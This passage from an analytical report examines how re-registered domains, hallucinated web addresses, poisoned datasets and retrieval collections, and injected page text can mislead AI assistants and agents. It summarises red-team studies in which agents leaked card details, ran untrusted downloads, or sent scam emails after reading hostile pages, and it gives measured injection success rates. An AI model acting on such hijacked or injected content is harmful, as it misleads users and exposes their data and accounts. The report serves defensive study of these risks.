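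The same description fits Hertz's packages and the tutorial in which the stranger changed only the package name. A filter that searches pages for hidden commands to the model would find none in either.

It is less clear how many agents read llms.txt at all. Ahrefs, which sells search-marketing tools, used server logs for its study *97% of llms.txt Files Never Get Read (137,000 Sites Analyzed)*. According to *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026), by Common Crawl, which archives the web, 28% of the domains in the Ahrefs study published the file. That is about 38,000 files, of which only about 1,150 received any request.

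The two findings are compatible. Most llms.txt files exist because software created them automatically. Common Crawl collected 584,107 and traced 68% to templates, with the website builder Wix alone responsible for 41%. Few programmers have reason to send an agent to a site such as a hairdresser's for documentation. Hertz chose large companies, many of which publish software or connect to it. A handful of heavily used files could account for his few dozen installations.

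Common Crawl also searched for instructions aimed at the model. It found ten files with apparent injections of the most serious kind, read them all and judged only four to be real. One was a security researcher's labelled trap, one asked the model to become a catgirl, one was a joke about crawler logs, and one told the model to bark like a dog and fetch another file. Common Crawl calls its abuse figures lower bounds because it searched for particular phrases. An install command with an unclaimed package name contains none of these phrases, so the search would have missed all 227 commands that Hertz found.

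About 2.5% of the llms.txt files, nearly 15,000, came from domains advertised for sale. An agent that requests documentation from one of these domains gets a sales pitch in the correct format. Common Crawl's *What is actually inside llms.txt*, the full report on the same files, calls the format "unguarded" partly for this reason. Another 1.4% still contained traces of a chatbot's draft, most often a blank where the company's name should have gone. If nobody read those drafts closely enough to fill in the name, some may also contain invented packages.

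The files also go out of date. One company's llms.txt listed Common Crawl's crawler as blocked, although the site's access rules allowed it. Package names and web addresses can become outdated in the same way when a company renames a product or gives up an old domain. Common Crawl's published measures cover what the files contain but not who owns the addresses in them, so it is unknown how many of those addresses point to a domain that has changed owners.

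### Addresses that the model recalls or invents

A language model can also produce an address that is not in any document it was given. Suppose the student asks a chatbot without a search tool where to find the Python Porch tutorials. The model may reproduce pythonporch.example from training data from the lecturer's time, or it may invent the phantom domain pythonporch-docs.example. The two addresses look equally plausible in the answer.

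The security company Netcraft tested a family of models, OpenAI's GPT-4.1, on addresses where a mistake could be costly. For Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, published in 2025, the researchers asked where to log in to 50 brands. They used ordinary questions, such as one from a user who had lost a bookmark. Over several rounds, the models gave 131 different hostnames (full site names, including any subdomain) on 97 domains:

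| Who held the domain | Number | Share of the 97 |
|---|---|---|
| The right brand | 64 | 66% |
| Nobody, or an owner with no active site | 28 | 29% |
| An unrelated business | 5 | 5% |

Netcraft's breakdown shows that the brands did not control 33 of the 97 domains the models gave, or 34%, though its headline applies that percentage to the 131 hostnames. The figure does not support Netcraft's conclusion that more than one in three users could end up on a site the brand doesn't own, because the company counted each domain once, however often the models gave it. If a model gives the right address nine times and a wrong one once, that counts as a 50% error rate, although only one answer in ten was wrong.

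Only the 28 empty domains matter for hijacking, and some of them were not available to register. A parked domain, for instance, has an owner but no real site. Netcraft's category also combines names the models invented with any real ones that had lapsed. Smaller institutions such as credit unions and regional banks fared worse than global brands, probably because they appear less often in training data.

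When Netcraft's researchers asked Perplexity, an AI search engine, for the Wells Fargo login page, the top link was a fake page on Google Sites, a free service for building websites. This example belongs under search results because the page existed and Perplexity had not invented its address. Google owned the domain, which had neither lapsed nor changed hands.

An attacker may also try to plant an address for models to repeat. Netcraft found a fake programming interface for Solana, a cryptocurrency network, that sent payments to the attacker's wallet. The attacker had promoted it through tutorials, forum answers and dozens of code repositories. At least five programmers had copied the code into their own public projects, some of which show signs of AI coding tools. Those tools may have supplied the code, but the programmers could also have copied it from a tutorial by hand.

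For *Phantom Squatting* (2026), Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, used an AI agent to study 913 brands and write 685,339 questions about their websites and services. The researchers put the questions to two small, low-cost models from 2025 and varied the temperature, which controls how far a model departs from its most likely next word. The answers contained 2.1 million web addresses, of which 13,229 (about 0.6%) were confirmed as malicious. The researchers also identified about 250,000 invented domains that were still unregistered.

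The number is large partly because of the questions Unit 42 asked. It wanted to simulate an attacker, so its agent wrote prompts to exploit known weaknesses, such as a model's tendency to accept a false premise and fill in the details. For example, asking about a portal that does not exist can lead the model to invent an address for it. The 250,000 domains therefore show how many names an attacker could collect, not how often ordinary users see one. Both companies also tested models that have since been replaced, so their figures may not hold for the assistants people use in late 2026.

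Most invented names are worthless to an attacker because no one will see them again. Unit 42 ranked them by two signs that a name would recur. The first is whether a model repeats the name at different temperatures, especially low ones, which make its answers most predictable. The second is whether different models give the same name for the same question. SC Media's *Attackers exploit AI-hallucinated web domains through 'phantom squatting'* (2026) reports that different models often give the same name. An attacker can therefore learn which names to buy by questioning a public chatbot.

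Unit 42 believes attackers are already doing this. It monitored registrations of the names it considered most dangerous and saw attackers acquire some of them 18 to 51 days after its system had predicted them. SC Media mentions two of these names, one resembling a national postal service's name and the other a bank's. In another case, an attacker built a phishing kit called Montana Empire with an AI coding assistant and used it on a domain that Unit 42 had flagged 23 days earlier.

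The models were released before anyone registered the malicious domains, so their predictions could not have come from data about the attacks. That timing does not show that the attackers got the names from a model. Criminals were making up plausible names for fake bank sites long before chatbots existed, and a model trained on the web will tend to generate similar ones. With a long enough list of predictions, some will match by chance. A fair test would compare registrations of the predicted names with registrations of equally plausible names that the models had not produced. The attacker used an AI coding assistant to write the kit, but that does not show where the name came from. Visitor records would also be needed to show that an AI system had sent anyone to these sites.

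Even if every one of these cases is what Unit 42 takes it to be, an invented domain gives its buyer something quite different from a re-registered one:

| | Re-registered domain | Invented domain |
|---|---|---|
| Earlier site | Yes, often with archived pages to copy | None |
| Links from other pages | Still in place | None at first |
| Search ranking | May carry over | None at first |
| Standing with security filters | May be good | None, good or bad |
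| How a buyer can choose it | By past traffic and links | By questioning models |

Unit 42 argues that attackers benefit from using a newly registered domain, because blocklists and reputation scores depend on past behaviour and the domain has none. Its researchers saw some of these domains go from registration to an active attack within hours. A strict filter could remove this advantage by treating every unknown domain as suspect, but it might still let pythonporch.example through because the lecturer spent ten years building the domain's good reputation.

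## Stored copies and citations that outlive their pages

An answer drawn from stored text depends on who controlled the domain when software collected that text. If the domain changes hands, the harm depends on whether this happens after someone vets the page but before its text is collected, or after collection but before a reader opens the citation.

Suppose a librarian reads the lecturer's installation tutorial on 12 January and adds its address to a list of recommended sources. Two colleges build assistants from that list, one in January and one in June.

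| Date | Event | First college's copy | Second college's copy |
|---|---|---|---|
| 12 January | The librarian vets the page | None yet | None yet |
| 20 January | The first college downloads the listed pages | Lecturer's text | None yet |
| 23 May | The stranger re-registers the domain and alters the package name | Lecturer's text | None yet |
| 2 June | The second college downloads the same list | Lecturer's text | Stranger's text |
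| 15 June | A student at each college asks what to install, then opens the citation | Right answer, hijacked link | Wrong answer, hijacked link |

At the first college, a student who follows the chatbot's answer comes to no harm, but one who checks the source will find a different package name and may trust the page over the chatbot. At the second college, checking the source doesn't help, because the page and the answer agree.

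A browsing agent fetches pages live, so years can pass between vetting and collection. If the user opens the link straight away, little time passes between collection and reading.

### Datasets published as lists of addresses

Researchers working on training data were the first to measure the danger of web content changing between vetting and download. In *Poisoning Web-Scale Training Datasets is Practical*, Carlini, Jagielski and colleagues (2023) studied ten image datasets whose makers publish a list of web addresses, each with a caption or a person's name, instead of the images. Storing the images would be expensive, and copying them raises privacy and copyright problems. Anyone training a model on such a dataset has to download the images, perhaps years after the makers collected them. The paper calls an attack that exploits this delay "split-view poisoning", because the makers and the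 later users see different content at the same address.

The researchers looked up every domain in May and August 2022, each time from two data centres, and counted it as expired only if all four lookups reported that the name did not exist. They then worked out how much of each dataset an attacker could control for $1,000 by starting with the domains that held the most images per dollar. Five of the datasets show the range:

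| Dataset | Release | Images on expired domains | Share an attacker could buy for $1,000 | Downloads per month |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FaceScrub | 2014 | 4.51% | at least 0.61% | at least 7 |
| CC-3M | 2018 | 1.04% | at least 0.08% | at least 29 |
| LAION-400M | 2021 | 0.71% | at least 0.05% | at least 10 |
| COYO-700M | 2022 | 1.51% | at least 0.10% | at least 5 |
| LAION-2B-en | 2022 | 0.29% | at least 0.01% | at least 7 |

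Older datasets generally had more images on expired domains. COYO-700M is an exception. Collecting it took nearly a year, and on the day of its release an attacker could already have bought expired domains hosting 0.1% of its images for less than $1,000.

At July 2023 prices, an attacker could control 0.01% of any of the datasets, or about 40,000 images in LAION-400M, for less than $60 a year. Earlier poisoning attacks often needed about that share of the data, but they were designed for an attacker who could also change the captions. Someone who buys an expired domain can change only the images.

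Carlini and colleagues got around this by choosing images whose captions already suited the attack. To make a model mistake an unrelated picture for an apple, they selected 1,000 images that were on purchasable domains and had "apple" in their captions, then replaced them all with that picture in their own copy of LAION-400M. They trained an image-recognition model on the result, and the attack worked for six of the ten labels they tried. A similar attack made a safety filter flag harmless pictures as unsafe in about 90% of cases. Each target required changing 0.00025% of the dataset.

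The attack also requires someone to download the images after the domain has changed hands. To find out whether people still did, the researchers bought six expired domains from each dataset, the three with the most images and three chosen at random. They answered all image requests with a "not found" error. About 15 million requests arrived each month. Many were unrelated to the datasets, so the researchers counted a download only if one IP address requested at least 90% of the dataset's images on their six domains, including at least one from each. At least half of that address's requests to those domains also had to be for images in the dataset.

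More than 800 downloads passed this test. The paper gives the logging period as twelve months in one place and six in another, so the rate is uncertain, but the downloads themselves are hard to dispute. Many visitors requested images in the same order as the dataset's list, and because that order is random, the only plausible explanation is that they were working through the list. The count probably missed anyone who spread a download over several IP addresses.

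The researchers found no sign that anyone had carried out such an attack. In CC-3M, for which they had the original images, only one domain with more than ten images had both a new owner and visibly different pictures, and it was serving advertisements. They searched LAION-400M less thoroughly, examining a few thousand of the more than four million domains with at least one changed image. A careful attacker who needed only 1,000 images could have escaped notice.

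Six of the ten datasets now come with fingerprints of the original images, so downloaders can reject any that have changed. LAION (2024), a non-profit organisation, computed fingerprints for its LAION-5B collection in early 2023 because of the study. It used them again when it reissued the collection in August 2024 after removing links to suspected child abuse images. *DataComp* (2023) introduced another large dataset, CommonPool, with fingerprints included to guard against poisoning.

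These measures let users detect a changed image, but they only partly solve the problem. *A Common Pool of Privacy Problems* (2025) explains that CommonPool still consists of 12.8 billion addresses, and that every user has to download the images afresh. Three other datasets came out without fingerprints even after Carlini and colleagues published the first version of their paper.

### Refreshing a retrieval collection

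The colleges' assistants look up the tutorial rather than train on it, which changes how an attacker can find domains to buy. When a training dataset's list is published, an attacker can see exactly which domains to buy. A college need not publish the list of sources its assistant uses, although the citations in the assistant's answers will reveal part of it.

However, the attacker needs to control far less material. Only the best-matching passages reach the model, so it hardly matters how much of the whole collection is hostile. *DenialRAG* (2026) cites earlier work in which a single poisoned document was enough to produce a wrong answer the attacker chose.

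*Towards Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026), a review of such attacks, uses the term "passive poisoning" for cases in which the attacker never breaks into the system's database. After the system's crawler has indexed the hostile content, the software must still select the passage for some question and the model must rely on it, so the review goes a little too far in treating the attack as effectively complete once the content is indexed. The stranger's tutorial would easily be selected, however, because it has almost the same words as the page it replaced and will match almost the same questions.

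Many collections are also refreshed on a schedule, and a refresh fetches the pages again without vetting them again. The next refresh after 23 May therefore replaces the first college's good copy with the stranger's version.

Commercial services differ in how they handle stored text when its page disappears. Amazon's Bedrock service lets customers build a searchable collection from websites. On every run, its crawler fetches every page in its scope, adds new and changed text, and removes text that is no longer there, according to AWS's *Crawl web pages for your knowledge base*. If the crawler can't tell whether a page is gone, it keeps the old text. Google Cloud's *Refresh web pages using automatic and manual refresh* describes a stricter rule, under which its service drops any page that returns an error.

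If the tutorial's address returned an error during the outage, Google's service would delete the lecturer's text and could later add the stranger's text as a new page. Amazon's service might keep the lecturer's text through the outage and then overwrite it with the stranger's. Both would end up with the wrong package name if they kept crawling the address.

Frequent refreshes are more likely to detect an outage, but they also collect a new owner's text sooner. In a data store that works from a sitemap (a site's own list of its pages), Google's service refreshes pages daily if the sitemap marks them as changed and every 14 days otherwise, according to Google Cloud's *Index and refresh web pages using sitemaps*. A crawler that visited every 14 days would find the tutorial site missing at least three times during its 43-day outage, and would collect the stranger's text within two weeks of its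 appearance. A crawler that visited every three months could keep the lecturer's text in use for longer, but it might miss the outage.

A predictable snapshot schedule can help an attacker who controls a page only briefly. Carlini and colleagues showed this with Wikipedia, which regularly publishes snapshots of its articles for reuse. They could usually predict to within about 30 minutes when the snapshot would reach a given article. From past editing records, they estimated that well-timed malicious edits could have got into the snapshot for 6.5% of English articles before other editors reverted them. Someone who re-registers a lapsed domain does not need such precise timing, because nobody else can revert the pages on it.

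Both commercial services also limit which sites a customer may include, while a team that writes its own crawler sets its own limits, if any. Amazon requires customers to crawl only their own pages or pages they have permission to crawl, and Google requires them to verify the domains in a sitemap. Under these rules, hijacked content is more likely to come from an old domain that the customer once owned and forgot to remove from the list than from an outsider's tutorial. But Amazon's crawler also fetches linked documents in supported formats, even from other domains, unless the customer excludes them. A PDF on a re-registered domain could therefore enter a company's collection because one of the company's own help pages still links to it.

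### Dead links in AI citations

Even if the stored text stays sound, the cited page may disappear or change. The most detailed study of such links is *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents* by Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch (2026). They requested each web address cited in existing answers to 100 research questions and recorded whether it returned an error or failed to connect. They did not count refusals of access as failures, since these usually come from sites that block automated visitors. They then looked up each failed address in the Wayback Machine, a public web archive. If the archive had ever saved a copy, they classed the link as stale, meaning that the page had once existed. Otherwise, they classed it as invented by the model.

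| System | Addresses | All failed links | Invented | Stale |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI deep research | 4,121 | 10.1% | 3.5% | 6.6% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro deep research | 11,309 | 18.5% | 13.3% | 5.2% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet with search | 641 | 7.8% | 3.0% | 4.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro with search | 1,609 | 5.9% | 4.8% | 1.1% |
| GPT-4.1 | 336 | 5.4% | 5.4% | 0.0% |

The stale links are the relevant ones here, because a page that has disappeared may have been on a domain that lapsed. Rao and colleagues take them as a sign that a system had searched the web through a partly outdated index. But the answers were already some months old, so some of the pages may have disappeared after a system cited them. The archive is also incomplete, so some of the "invented" addresses were probably real pages that it had never saved.

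The paper reports 53,090 addresses for this part of the study, but the counts for its ten systems add up to only 23,269. The larger number may include the 13 other systems in the benchmark, which the researchers excluded. In a second test, three newer models produced 168,021 addresses in response to 2,177 questions written by experts, and 8.2% of the addresses failed. The highest failure rate was 17.4%, for Claude Sonnet 4.5 on healthcare and medicine.

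Link failure rates vary widely between models. In *Cited but Not Verified* (2026), one of 2,159 links from OpenAI's GPT-5.4 failed, compared with 19.2% of those from Llama 4 Maverick, an open model. The study counted blocked pages as failures, so its figures are not directly comparable with those of Rao and colleagues.

The definition of a dead link matters just as much in larger surveys by marketing firms. Law (2025), in *New Study*, reports that 2.38% of the addresses cited by ChatGPT returned a "page not found" error, compared with a baseline of 0.84%. OtterlyAI (2026), which sells monitoring of AI search, classed 19.3% of 20 million cited addresses as gone, but its definition also includes pages that had moved or could not be reached.

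None of these studies recorded who owned the domains, so the share of AI citations that lead to re-registered domains is unknown. A hijacked page that loads normally counts as a working link. A link checker would report the tutorial as dead during the outage and as working again from 23 May, so re-registration lowers the measured rate of dead links. As a remedy, Rao and colleagues gave models a tool for testing links and replacing the bad ones, which cut GPT-5.1's failure rate from 16.0% to 0.6%, but the tool would also accept the stranger's page because it loads normally.

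A link can also keep working after its content has changed. Carlini and colleagues compared the 3.3 million images in CC-3M, first downloaded in 2018, with what the same addresses served in 2023. About 2.9 million still loaded, but only 1.1 million of those were identical to the original files. Resizing or re-encoding an image is enough to change the file, so these figures don't show how many changes were hostile.

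An experiment that OtterlyAI published in July 2026 shows more clearly how long a citation can outlast its page. A company deleted 15 pages of product comparisons on known dates, and OtterlyAI checked daily whether seven AI search engines still cited them. The citations continued for weeks, and for more than eight months for one older batch. The test covered only one company's pages, and the company still owned its domain. But if citations to the tutorial lasted eight months after the site went offline on 7 April, they would continue until early December. By then the stranger would have owned the domain for more than six months.

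## What a hijacked page can do to the system that reads it

From 23 May, any AI system that opens pythonporch.example receives the stranger's text. The harm depends on what the system can do. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) divides an attack on an agent into a "source", which is a way to influence the system, and a "sink", which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. A re-registered domain is a source, and the sinks vary by system. A chatbot that can only answer may mislead its user, an assistant with access to email may leak it, and an agent that can run commands or spend money may do damage directly.

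### Systems that can only answer

A system that can only write answers can still repeat a falsehood or recommend a dangerous link. In the lecturer's case, it gives the student the wrong package name and supports it by citing a site with a ten-year reputation.

In June 2026 Netcraft measured how often AI answer engines return malicious links. It asked ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity, as an ordinary customer might, how to reach the login pages of several of the world's largest banks and retail brands. The 2,905 answers contained 20,706 links. Netcraft classed 0.28% of the links (about 58) as malicious, and 1.7% of the answers (about 49) contained at least one. Perplexity returned the most.

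These rates are low, but someone who asks for a bank's login page is about to type in a password. In one Copilot answer, the first link led to an imitation of the Wells Fargo login page. A question about the official website of Kohl's, an American department store, led to a fake shop.

Netcraft's 2025 test, on models without a search tool, mostly turned up invented or empty addresses. The malicious links in the 2026 test led to live sites that attackers controlled and that the engines had found on the web. The two tests covered different kinds of system, so they don't show that invented addresses have become rarer. Netcraft also gives no count of re-registered domains. The fake Wells Fargo page was on a domain that misspelled the bank's name and had no good reputation to inherit, but it still came first in the answer.

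A system can repeat a false statement from a page as easily as a link. Netcraft recounts that in February 2026 a technology journalist got several major search engines to describe him as the best hot dog eater in his profession by publishing a single page on his own website. This was easier because nobody else had published anything on the subject, whereas a false package name would have to compete with other tutorials that give the right one.

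The engines in the Fudan University study filtered out traditional search spam, but according to Netcraft, the study found that text written specifically for AI retrieval doubled the rate at which manipulated content reached the engines' answers.

Stored collections have the same weakness once they contain a false page. In *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks*, Li, Zhou and colleagues (2025) added one false document to a collection of more than 10,000 chemical recipes. They asked PaperQA, a research assistant that answers from scientific papers, for the best way to make a certain compound. It retrieved the false document in all 100 trials. The document matched the question unusually well because it described its own method as the best, but anyone who writes a hostile page can do the same.

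### Systems that hold private data

The main experiments in that paper tested Computer Use, an Anthropic agent that operates a computer much as a person would. Li and colleagues gave the agent a credit card number and an address to look after. They built a website for a refrigerator that did not exist, with a form asking for card details, and wrote Reddit posts that linked to it. The agent gave away the private details in all ten trials that started from one of these posts, but in none of the ten where the researchers gave it the website's address directly.

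Li and colleagues conclude that the attack depends on the trust agents place in established platforms. Their experiment can't establish that, because the Reddit posts also contained instructions to the agent, and supplying the address directly removed both the platform and the instructions. Testing a Reddit post with only the link, and a post with the same instructions on an unknown site, would have separated the effects of the platform and the instructions.

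The trials also began with the agent already looking at the post, so they don't account for the chance that the agent would never have found it. The researchers chose an obscure product to keep real shoppers away.

An agent inside the user's own browser may be able to reach far more than a card number. Since 1995, browsers have applied the same-origin policy, which prevents one website from reading another's data, such as a webmail inbox open in another tab. Researchers at the University of Washington tested seven browsers with built-in AI agents, according to Darinor's *The Same-Origin Policy Is Only as Strong as Your Browser Agent* (2026). In four of them, an injection on one page could use the agent to read data from other sites. The policy does not stop this because the agent has access to both sites on the user's behalf. A student who asks such an agent to read the hijacked Python tutorial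 could expose their email inbox.

### Systems that can act

Li and colleagues used the same route through Reddit to test whether Computer Use would run a program from an unknown source. They presented the program as a VPN client, which is software for private internet connections, and deliberately made the download site look suspicious. The agent downloaded and ran the file in all ten trials.

In ten further trials, researchers gave the agent the login for an email account and led it to a page containing a scam message for it to send. The agent sent the message to the user's parent every time, asking for money in five trials and card details in the other five. Such a message is more dangerous than ordinary spam because it comes from the real account of someone the recipient knows.

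OpenAI got a similar result in its own testing, when it trained a language model to search for attacks on the agent in its Atlas browser. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes one attack that worked. The user asked for an out-of-office reply, but while preparing it the agent read a hostile email and sent the user's resignation to the chief executive instead. The instructions arrived by email, but OpenAI lists web pages as another place where an agent may encounter them. It has since trained the agent to resist attacks of this kind.

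All these attacks relied on instructions aimed at the agent, but coding agents needed no such instructions to install the packages that Hertz registered under names in companies' llms.txt files.

### What site owners have actually planted

Researchers who build an attack choose its purpose themselves. To learn what people put on real websites, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses from Common Crawl's October 2025 archive for 3,963 phrases typical of injections. They added results from two services that scan the internet for servers. Two reviewers then worked through the 31,206 matches, many of them in groups of near-identical cases, to remove tutorials, news reports and other harmless mentions. They confirmed 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages:

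| Apparent aim | Injections |
|---|---|
| Disrupt or degrade the AI system's work | 8,894 |
| of which: have it carry out a destructive command | 157 |
| Forbid the reuse of personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 |
| Expose a visitor as a bot | 3,096 |
| Override the task, with no clear purpose | 2,632 |
| Promote a product, person or source | 1,521 |
| Extract secrets | 13 |

Some injections appear in more than one row. Most of the disruptive ones only try to make a model produce nonsense, apparently to hinder programs that copy the site. Attempts to steal or to run destructive commands, the worst outcomes, make up about 1% of the total.

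Injections of any kind are also rare. In the Common Crawl data they appeared on 9,676 pages, or about one in 124,000. An agent that read 100 random pages a day would take more than three years, on average, to come across one. The true number is higher because the search missed injections in images, in most other languages and in unfamiliar wording, and those on pages that show their instructions only to AI agents. The number may also be growing. Khodayari and colleagues cite a Google report that malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.

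Four fifths of the injections in the Common Crawl data came from the sites' own operators. More than half of those were in HTTP response headers, which a person reading the page never sees. User contributions such as comments accounted for only 1.8%. Someone who re-registers a domain becomes its operator and can put injections in any of these places, whereas Li and colleagues had to start from posts on someone else's platform.

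To test whether the injections work, the researchers picked 100 at random and had 13 models summarise the pages containing them, giving them each page in four formats. The models followed the injection in 81 of 5,200 runs (1.6%), including six in which the model also pointed it out. The rate was 8% for small models that received only a page's plain text, and 0.6% for closed commercial models across all formats. Plain text is the riskiest format because stripping out the page's code removes the signs that a passage was hidden from human readers.

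These rates are a poor guide to what a determined attacker could achieve. Most of the texts were crude, and 54 templates accounted for 95% of them. Summarising a page is also simpler than an agent's usual work, and the researchers did not test whether a model that followed the instructions would also misuse a tool.

### What a re-registered domain adds

Any new website could carry the same hostile text, but the buyer of an old domain hopes that an AI system will be more likely to find the page and treat it as reliable. The old domain may still have its search ranking, links from respected sites, and a name that the model learned in training.

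Of these, the ranking has the most direct evidence, from AIR's search results and Brockbank's casino sites. The claim that the domains' history caused those rankings is still an inference.

How much an inherited link helps someone attack an AI system is still mostly inferred. For links from respected sites, the closest measurement is the difference Li and colleagues found between agents arriving from Reddit and agents arriving directly. Even if the platform caused the whole difference, the result would not transfer neatly to the university's reading list. The list probably deserves more trust than an anonymous post, but it only recommends something to read, while the Reddit posts contained instructions for the agent.

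The evidence is thinnest on whether a model treats a page as more reliable because its domain is familiar. Netcraft and Unit 42 measured which addresses models produce from memory, but did not test this. The effect seems plausible, since the training data may contain both the lecturer's tutorials and other people's praise for them. A model trained on the old site might also detect that the new content doesn't fit, which would help against a casino page but not much against the stranger's copy.

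### How well current models resist injection

Developers report that recent models resist injection much better than the agent that Li and colleagues tested in early 2025. The most detailed figures come from the system card for Claude Opus 5, the safety report that Anthropic published with the model in July 2026. For browser use, Anthropic built 129 test environments containing attacks by professional testers and made sure that the model would see each attack. The attacker had ten attempts in each. Anthropic ran the models alone and then with "auto mode", its strongest protection, which checks incoming material for injected instructions and separately blocks dangerous actions. The results below are for models using extended reasoning:

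| Model | Successful attempts, model alone | Environments breached, model alone | Environments breached, auto mode |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 81 of 129 | 1 of 129 |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 29.7% | 71 of 129 | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.93% | 9 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

The zeros are impressive, though a run of 129 without a breach would not be surprising even if 2% of similar situations were vulnerable. The first two columns matter most to developers who build their own agents without checking incoming material, as Anthropic's own product, Claude Cowork, always does. These columns also show how much models from one company can differ, since attacks succeeded about eight times as often against Mythos 5 as against Opus 5. Anthropic has since released newer models.

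Comparisons between companies are harder to interpret. Anthropic also reports results from a benchmark that the security firm Gray Swan built with British and American government institutes and several developers. The benchmark estimates the chance that an attacker succeeds within 15 attempts. That chance was 2.0% for Opus 5 and 20.0% for Sol, the most capable version of OpenAI's GPT-5.6. It was higher for the smaller versions, at 30.4% for Terra and 43.9% for Luna.

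OpenAI's tests ranked the three versions in the opposite order. Attacks hidden in material the agent processed succeeded in 3.77% of attempts against Sol, 3.32% against Terra and 2.94% against Luna, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, which covers an August 2026 update. A model's ranking evidently depends a good deal on which attacks the testers use. Anthropic warns that fixed sets of known attacks can give a false sense of security.

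Outsiders can still compromise AI agents. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that four research teams broke AI agents in ten days in July 2026, and that Claude for Chrome was among the targets. *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark from PromptArmor, which sells AI security, records successful attacks on leading models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon.

An attack with a low success rate per attempt is also more dangerous on a web page than in a single email, because thousands of agents can read the page over time and its owner can first test different wordings on publicly available models.

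OpenAI wrote in December 2025 that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and compared it to scams aimed at people. In March 2026 it added that most of the attacks it sees against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses. It also reported that the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, which manipulates people with plausible stories. Filters that screen incoming text usually miss these attacks, because recognising such an attack is as hard as recognising a lie. OpenAI therefore also tries to limit the damage when an attack succeeds.

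All the success rates above measure how often a model obeys hostile instructions. The stranger's tutorial contains no such instructions, so a model that never obeys them could still tell the student to install the wrong package.

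## Whether the human findings carry over, premise by premise

The best measurements of residual trust come from people and ordinary software. To apply them to AI systems, one has to accept four premises:

1. References to lapsed domains survive in the places where AI systems look for pages.
2. AI systems follow those references.
3. They do not notice that the owner has changed.
4. What they read there changes what they say or do.

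If any premise is false, the risk disappears. A premise that holds only some of the time makes the risk smaller.

### References to lapsed domains survive

People return to an old site because they bookmarked it or remember its name. An AI agent often starts a task with no memory of earlier ones, so it may seem to have no habits that a domain's new owner could exploit.

But residual trust never depended on habit alone. As So and colleagues describe it, it also covers visitors who had never used the old site and found it through a forum post or a search result. An agent that takes the tutorial's address from the university's reading list is in the same position. A model can also retain addresses from its training. When Netcraft asked models for login pages, they gave addresses from memory. An outdated address is harder to remove from a model already in use than from a person's bookmarks.

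Many users asking similar questions can have the same effect as one user's habit. In *Do AI Assistants Fetch Empty Pages More?*, Watanabe and Nakayashiki (2026) used server logs from their own company's site, glasp.co, which publishes summaries of YouTube videos. They tracked ChatGPT-User, the program that opens pages for people using ChatGPT, for four weeks from 27 October 2026. It returned most often to the pages it had opened most in the previous two weeks.

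Old references are also common. In *When 200 OK Is Not an Answer*, Zhang (2026) requested 4,795 web addresses cited in ExpertQA, a set of expert-checked answers from 2023. By October 2026, 11.8% were dead, based on the server's response or a missing DNS record. Including addresses that still loaded but showed an error message, an unrelated page or a parked domain raised the figure to 16.0%. Zhang did not count lapsed domains separately, so most of these may be deleted pages on domains that never changed hands.

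### AI systems follow those references

Agents reach many pages through search, and search engines demote spam. If Google moves a spam site on a re-registered domain down to the fifth page of results, an agent that opens only the top few results won't find it through that search.

But the engine has to crawl the new content first, which can take a long time for obscure pages. Of the pages that ChatGPT-User opened on glasp.co, 57.8% had received no confirmed visit from Google's or Bing's crawler in the previous three to four weeks, and 41.3% had received none over the full 49 days of logs. The tutorial site's outage lasted 43 days, so a crawler that visits this rarely could miss it. These figures come from only one site, though, and it has a very large number of little-read pages. A crawler might also detect that a whole domain is offline without checking each page.

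The domain's age may also help the new owner. Infoblox warns that reputation-based algorithms may favour an old name over a new one, according to Security Affairs' *Crooks Are Buying Your Expired Domains and Using Them to Deliver Malware*. Frieß and colleagues attribute the high search rankings of hijacked subdomains to the parent domain's history. In their data, 98.5% of the parent domains were more than a year old and most were more than ten, though this could also be because older organisations have more forgotten DNS records to hijack.

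Search therefore removes some hijacked pages but not all of them. To learn how many remain, one would want to know how often AI systems request old addresses, and published figures come only partway:

- seoClarity, which sells search-marketing software, reports that 2% to 3% of requests from ChatGPT's bots run into a missing page, a broken redirect or a block.
- SEOmator's *Crawl Waste Report 2026* (2026) quotes a much worse figure from the network company Cloudflare, whose data showed only 45.9% of crawler requests returning a page normally in July. But this covers crawlers of every kind, and the failures include deliberate blocks and ordinary redirects.
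- TollBit's *Bits and Bots* (2025) counts people who clicked a link in an AI answer and reached a missing page. For Anthropic the rate fell from 55% to 4.8% in the year to the second quarter of 2025, a period in which Claude gained access to the live web. OpenAI's rose from 0.3% to 3.7% in a single quarter.
- Law found a lower rate for ChatGPT, 1.01% of clicked addresses. The figure for Google was 0.15%, according to Search Engine Journal.

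These figures cannot include visits to lapsed domains, because they come from the records of working websites and a lapsed domain has no server to record a failed visit. The AI companies could count how often their own fetchers look up a name that no longer exists. After a domain is re-registered, its new owner has the visitor log.

The glasp.co logs hint at what agents do when a page has no useful content. Watanabe and Nakayashiki had expected ChatGPT-User to return more often to summary pages with no article than to pages with one, but its return rate was 16% lower for the empty pages in the main analysis. The gap shrank to 4% when the researchers counted every fetch, and there was no clear difference among the pages it had opened most before the study, so the agent did not clearly avoid empty pages. Readers of the lapsed sports news site, by contrast, were gone within a month. The comparison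 is rough because the empty pages still loaded and their site still had its original owner.

The study provides almost no evidence about other assistants. Cloudflare could verify almost none of the requests that claimed to come from Claude's equivalent program, and none of those that claimed to come from Perplexity's. The counts also exclude agents that do not identify themselves.

### AI systems do not notice the new owner

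A model may detect a mismatch that a hurried person would miss. It can read the whole page, including text too small or faint for a person to see, and it may have learned in training what the site used to contain.

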